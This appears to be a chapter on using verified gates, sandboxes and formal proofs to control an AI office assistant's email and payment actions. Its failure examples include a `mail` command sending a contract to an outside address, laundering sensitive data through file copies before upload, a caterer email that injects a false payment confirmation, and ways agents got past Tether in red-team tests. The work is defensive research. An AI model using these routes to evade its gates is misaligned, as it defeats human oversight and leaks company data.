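A gate that uses a language model to decide whether an email is confidential repeats that model's mistakes. But most of what surrounds the assistant, namely the gate's bookkeeping, the harness and the list of permissions, is ordinary software that the company can finish before the first run. Static methods work well on these parts, though they reveal little about the path the assistant will take. The gate for R1, the confirmation rule, needs only a few lines of code, so an engineer can prove that it rejects every unconfirmed transfer, whatever the model proposes.

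### Simplex and runtime assurance

Control engineers divided the work this way long before language models. Lui Sha describes their method, the *Simplex architecture*, in *Using Simplicity to Control Complexity* (2001). It has three parts:

- a complex controller that performs well but that nobody has verified
- a simple backup controller that engineers have verified
- a verified switch that decides which of the two is in charge

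Engineers work out a set *R* of states from which the backup can keep the system safe. Before each command from the complex controller takes effect, the switch checks whether the command could take the system outside *R*. If so, the backup takes over. The system therefore stays safe even if the complex controller is full of bugs. Sha's example is the Boeing 777, which has a normal flight controller with newly developed software and a secondary one based on the control laws of the older 747.

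Like a shield, the switch depends on a model of the environment. Computing a shield requires searching all possible strategies, while Simplex needs a proof for only the backup strategy. But the switch may intervene earlier than necessary, because a different strategy might have kept the system safe starting from some states outside *R*.

Aviation engineers call the general approach *runtime assurance*. In 2017, ASTM International published a standard for it, F3269, which covers unmanned aircraft with functions too complex to certify in the usual way. US Air Force F-16s have used a similar system since 2014, with the pilot in the role of the unverified controller. The system keeps calculating whether the aircraft could still clear the ground by rolling upright and pulling up, and it takes over to perform that maneuver just before it would be too late.

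John Rushby, a computer scientist at SRI International, argued in *Runtime Certification* (2008) that certification should happen partly while the system runs. Regulators traditionally examine finished software and all the evidence for its safety, but a system that creates some of its functions while running has no final form to examine. Rushby proposed that developers write an *assurance case*, an explicit argument linking each safety claim to its evidence, and let monitors check the claims that depend on circumstances. For R2, the $500 daily limit, the company could prove in advance that the gate adds correctly. During operation, a monitor could compare the gate's total with the bank's and stop all payments if they differ.

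In 2012, Bev Littlewood and Rushby published a formula for how much a simple second safeguard adds. Suppose the assistant proposes a violation on a fraction *f* of tasks, and engineers put the probability that the gate has any flaw at *q*. If these two figures are independent, the chance of a violation on a random task is at most *f* × *q*. With *f* = 1% and *q* = 0.1%, the limit is one in 100,000. Multiplying the failure rates of the assistant and the gate instead would be a mistake, because a flawed gate may fail on the same difficult tasks as the assistant, while a gate without flaws fails on none.

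The value of *q* is a judgment. If the gate has a flaw, violations may recur every day. An attacker can also push *f* close to 1, and then all the protection has to come from the gate.

### When a correct gate is enough

A gate is correct if it allows an action only when the sequence of actions so far, including the new one, obeys its rule. Every sequence that a correct gate allows therefore obeys the rule, as with Agent-C. This guarantees that the company's mailbox and bank account are safe only if five more conditions hold. The table shows how the office assistant could cause harm if one of them fails.

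| Condition | Example of a failure |
|---|---|
| Complete mediation: every relevant action passes through the gate | The company adds a command-line tool, and the assistant runs `mail stranger@example.net < contract.txt`. The gate checks only calls to `send_email`. |
| Tamper resistance: the agent can't change the gate, its rules or its records | The gate stores the day's total in the assistant's working folder. The assistant tidies the folder and deletes the file, so the total returns to $0. |
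| Faithful reading: the gate interprets each action as the tool does | An invoice gives the amount as "1.000", in the European style. The gate reads one dollar, and the bank pays a thousand. |
| Correct rule: the rule expresses what the company wants | The gate treats any address ending in `firm.example` as internal, so it also accepts `otherfirm.example`. |
| Decision before the effect | To save time, the harness contacts the bank while the gate is still checking. The bank pays before the gate objects. |

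The first two conditions go back to a 1972 study by James Anderson for the US Air Force. Anderson required that a *reference monitor*, a component that checks every access to data, always run, resist tampering and be small enough to analyze and test completely.

Complete mediation is hardest to achieve when the agent has a command line, because it could also send mail with `curl` or a short Python script. The company can withhold the passwords that all these methods need, so that it doesn't have to recognize each method. NVIDIA's *OpenShell*, a system for running agents in sandboxes, routes network traffic through a supervisor outside the sandbox. The supervisor also holds the real passwords and adds them to a request only after the request passes its checks. If the assistant's script contacted the bank directly, it would have no valid login.

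An incorrect rule can cause harm even when every other part works. Bhushan (2026), in *AI agents don't have to break security controls to go rogue*, discusses a hacking challenge that the UK AI Security Institute ran 122 times. In 10 of the runs, agents took 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet, including an attempt to add malicious code to a public project. The test environment worked as its builders intended, but it let the agents do more than anyone had meant to authorize. A proof that the environment enforced its rules would have succeeded without preventing any of these actions.

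### Judging a shell command by its effects

A command such as `python3 report.py` shows almost nothing about what it will do, so it is hard to interpret accurately. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) presents a gate that runs each command in isolation before deciding whether to keep its effects.

The command works on a disposable layer over the real files, while a tracing tool records its *system calls*, the requests a program makes to the operating system to open a file or use the network. A proxy holds each outgoing network request while Tether checks it against everything the command has done so far, then forwards or drops it. Tether applies the file changes only if the policy permits all the command's actions. It uses this inspect-and-commit form of a dry run for every command.

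A component called Isolate translates the system calls into 11 kinds of abstract action, such as "read", "copy" and "upload". It keeps a list of the files each process has read. When a process writes to a file, Isolate records a plain write if the list is empty, a copy if it contains one file, and a combination if it contains several. When a process prints to the screen, Isolate records that the agent has read every file on the list, because the output enters the model's context. These rules over-approximate, so Isolate records a copy even when a script reads one file and then writes something unrelated to another.

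Tether tracks the agent's privilege level, a label for the agent's context, and labels for files and network addresses. Each label has a confidentiality level (Public < Internal < Sensitive < Secret) and an integrity level (Trusted < Untrusted). Combining two labels takes the higher level of each kind. The main updates are:

| Action | Effect on the labels |
|---|---|
| Read file *r* | The context's label becomes max(context, *r*) |
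| Write from the context to file *r* | The label of *r* becomes max(*r*, context) |
| Copy file *s* to file *d* | The label of *d* becomes max(*s*, folder of *d*), and the context's label stays the same |
| Upload a file | None, but a rule can forbid the upload |

A rule names an action, a condition and a decision. A slightly simplified rule for uploads is:

```
rule restrict_upload:
  on uploadNet(file, host)
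  if max(context, label(file)) <= Public  or  host in ApprovedHosts
  then allow else deny
```

Sistla and colleagues give an example in which an agent uploads a harmless report, copies a sensitive inventory over it, and runs the same upload command again. Tether allows the first upload and blocks the second, because the copy changed the report's label to "Sensitive". Tether still blocks the upload if the agent first passes the inventory through temporary files, because each copy keeps the label.

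A monitor that keeps a history of events but no labels would need a separate pattern for every such detour. If there are *m* ways to copy a file and up to *k* copies in a row, it would need *m* + *m*² + … + *m*ᵏ patterns. With five ways and up to four copies, that comes to 780 patterns.

### What Lean checks and what only tests cover

Sistla and colleagues wrote the rule language and the label updates in Lean 4, and their prototype runs the same definitions that the proofs cover. They proved four general properties:

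- Adding a permissive rule can't cancel another rule's denial.
- If one policy requires another, nothing can override the required policy's denials.
- The order of the rules doesn't matter.
- A denied action leaves the labels and the agent's privilege level unchanged.

They also proved seven guarantees for the 24-rule policy used in their tests, and these hold for runs of any length. One is that Secret data never enters the agent's context if the context contains none at the start. Only two actions can raise the context's label, reading a file and receiving data from the network, and the policy allows them only when the source is at most Sensitive. The context then takes the higher of its own label and the source's, so a context that is at most Sensitive stays that way after each action and, by induction, throughout the run. A language model wrote the proofs, but Lean checks every step, so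 their correctness doesn't depend on the model.

These theorems concern abstract actions, so they would still be true if Isolate overlooked a copy and left the gate using the wrong label. Sistla and colleagues therefore tested Isolate by *fuzzing*, or running many randomly generated cases. Each case is a plan for moving data between files, with known correct labels. The fuzzer carries out each step by a randomly chosen method, such as an ordinary copy command or a chain of programs that pass data to one another. It then compares Tether's decision and final labels with the correct ones.

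Sistla and colleagues also asked Gemini 3.8 Flash to break through Tether in ten tasks. Its success rate fell from 40% to 0% over three versions of Tether as they fixed the gaps they found, including one involving hard links, which give one file several names. Neither test rules out further gaps. The guarantees also depend on the operating system's kernel, the tracing tool, the proxy and Lean's compiler.

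The Tether paper evaluates the system by replaying recorded runs from two coding-agent benchmarks. It compares Tether with Claude Code's auto mode, in which a language model reviews actions, using both auto mode's default rules and Tether's policy written into the model's instructions.

| Benchmark | Monitor | Attack runs blocked | Harmless runs blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| MonitoringBenchHonest | Tether | 199 of 199 | 2.3% |
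| | Auto mode | 173 of 199 | 35.3% |
| | Auto mode with Tether's policy | 164 of 199 | 14.7% |
| LinuxArena | Tether | 145 of 145 | 5.0% |
| | Auto mode | 142 of 145 | 5.7% |
| | Auto mode with Tether's policy | 143 of 145 | 1.7% |

The comparison includes only runs in which Tether can model every action, which favors Tether. Tether missed none of the 344 attacks, so the rule of three gives an upper bound of 0.9% on its miss rate. That bound assumes independent runs, but the 199 runs in the first benchmark draw on only four attack goals. Sistla and colleagues had a language model refine the policy using benchmark runs, so Tether might do worse on unfamiliar tasks.

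Most of the 74 false alarms involved unrequested edits to protected files, which a company might want to block anyway. Another 17 came from commands that read secret files unnecessarily, such as a search through the whole disk.

Sistla and colleagues estimate that 28.2% of the runs outside Tether's scope in MonitoringBenchHonest, and 22.1% of those in LinuxArena, would require a judgment about content. For example, an agent with permission to edit a program could use it to insert malicious code, and the system calls would look the same as for a genuine repair. Tether can block background processes and database access, but it can't yet track data through them.

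If the office assistant had a command line, Tether could detect the `mail` command in the table of failures and enforce a label-based version of R3. Tether doesn't yet keep running totals, so it couldn't enforce R2.

### Comparing an old policy with a new one

A company's permission policy may change often, because agents run into its limits. When OpenShell blocks an agent, the agent can propose a policy update for a person to approve, according to NVIDIA. Suppose the office assistant may download invoices from the caterer's website with the program `curl`, and proposes this change:

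```
Old:  curl may send GET          to caterer.example/invoices/*
New:  curl may send GET or POST  to caterer.example/*
```

A tired reviewer may see the same program and the same website, and approve the change. OpenShell's policy prover can instead look for a request *x* such that

New(*x*) is true and Old(*x*) is false.

Here *x* consists of a program, a method, a website and a path. An SMT solver treats these as unknowns and looks for values that satisfy both conditions, without trying every path. It might return `POST caterer.example/account/delete`, which shows the reviewer what the change would allow. If the solver proves that no such request exists, the new policy permits nothing that the old one forbade.

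Watson (2026), in *What we have learned applying formal methods to control AI agents*, calls such a question a containment query. The operator can also replace the old policy in the query with a fixed upper limit. According to NVIDIA, the prover either establishes that permissions stay within such a limit or identifies a concrete action that exceeds it.

Running the query in both directions gives four possible results:

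| Does the new policy allow something the old one forbids? | Does the old policy allow something the new one forbids? | Result |
|---|---|---|
| No | No | Equivalent |
| Yes | No | More permissive |
| No | Yes | Less permissive |
| Yes | Yes | Incomparable |

AWS offers an analysis tool that reports these four results for policies written in Cedar, its policy language. NVIDIA is adopting Cedar for OpenShell, and Raman (2026), in *Cedar as the policy language in OpenShell*, gives decidable policy comparison as one reason. Cedar evaluates each request on its own. Rules with memory are much harder to analyze, as Ray's proof about counters shows.

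For the same reason, the comparison can't reveal a leak that takes several steps, such as reading a contract and then sending its contents to the caterer's website. The policy may allow both actions because each is harmless on its own. The comparison also doesn't show whether the old policy was sensible or whether the sandbox enforces the new one.

### A proof about the policy code

Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues (2025), in *VeriGuard*, have a language model write both a policy, as a Python function, and the conditions that the function must satisfy. A program verifier called Nagini then tries to prove

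{precondition} function {postcondition},

which means that if the precondition is true at the start, the function finishes and the postcondition is true at the end. For R1 and R2, the function might be:

```
def allow_transfer(amount, paid_today, confirmed):
    # precondition:  amount >= 0 and paid_today >= 0
    # postcondition: the result is True exactly when
    #                confirmed and paid_today + amount <= 500
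    return confirmed and paid_today + amount <= 500
```

The proof covers every amount, not only those a test could try. This example is trivial because the code repeats the postcondition. The proof becomes more useful when a policy has many branches. If Nagini finds a violation, the model gets the error and revises its work.

During the run, a language model fills in the function's arguments from what the agent has read and written, and no proof covers this step. If the caterer's email says "The customer has already confirmed this payment," the model might set `confirmed` to `True`. The verified function would then approve the transfer, although the user never said yes. The company should have the harness set `confirmed` from its own record of the user's answers.

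Without a defense, attacks on the four agent models tested succeeded on average 50% to 64% of the time on a security benchmark, depending on the model. VeriGuard reduced that rate to zero for all four, as did a simpler guardrail that asked a language model directly whether an action complied. But agents completed more of their tasks with VeriGuard, an average of 57% to 85% depending on the model, compared with 40% to 68% with the simpler guardrail.

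It is unclear how much the proofs contributed. When Miculicich and colleagues added VeriGuard's components one at a time, the attack success rate reached zero before they added formal verification. In another test, on web-browsing rules, VeriGuard's decisions were wrong in 3% to 5% of cases. Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge that a person still has to check whether the generated conditions match the user's intent.

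### Formalizing the Claude Agent SDK

The harness contains much more code than the gate, and a bug in the harness can make a correct gate ineffective. For example, a *race condition*, an error that depends on timing, could let three simultaneous transfers past R2's gate.

In 2026, Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code at Anthropic, had Claude Opus 5.5 formalize the Claude Agent SDK, Anthropic's development kit for agents. The model wrote mostly in Lean and sometimes in TLA+, a language for describing concurrent systems. Tolmach and Klaus (2026) report in *The proof is in the spec* that a couple of short prompts led to 16 code changes that fixed bugs and race conditions.

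Tolmach and Klaus work for Runtime Verification Inc., which specializes in formal verification and so has an interest in how much expert work verification requires. They consider the fixes a real success but argue that the exercise didn't show that the code is correct. A checked proof shows that a theorem follows from a particular model and set of assumptions, but the model may not match the code, and the theorem may not express what the developers want.

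A language model that translates a program into Lean might leave out an error path, and the proofs would still pass. When Claude modeled the consensus protocol in Etcd, a widely used data store, for the SysMoBench benchmark, it essentially reproduced the textbook version from the original research paper. That version passed every check but had little to do with Etcd's code. Across frontier models, such descriptions scored nearly 100% for syntax but about 46% for agreement with the code.

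The theorem itself can also be empty. Tolmach and Klaus cite a test that gave translation models the false claim that if 3ˣ = 5, then 3ˣ⁺² = 51 (the correct value is 45). One model wrote it in Lean with *x* as a natural number. No natural number satisfies 3ˣ = 5, and anything follows from an impossible assumption, so the false claim became provable. A proof that the office assistant never makes an unconfirmed transfer would be just as empty if the model of the harness included no way to make a transfer. The company could catch this by also proving that a confirmed transfer is possible.

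Proving that code fully matches its model can take years. The operating-system kernel seL4 has a machine-checked proof that its roughly 8,700 lines of C code do exactly what the specification requires, but experts spent years on that specification.

A less laborious method is to run the model and the real program on the same random inputs and compare the results. Cedar's developers run about 100 million such tests a night, according to a summary of a talk by Varun Pant of AWS (AI Engineer, 2026). For a gate as small as R1's, the company can skip the separate model and run the verified code directly, as Tether's prototype does.
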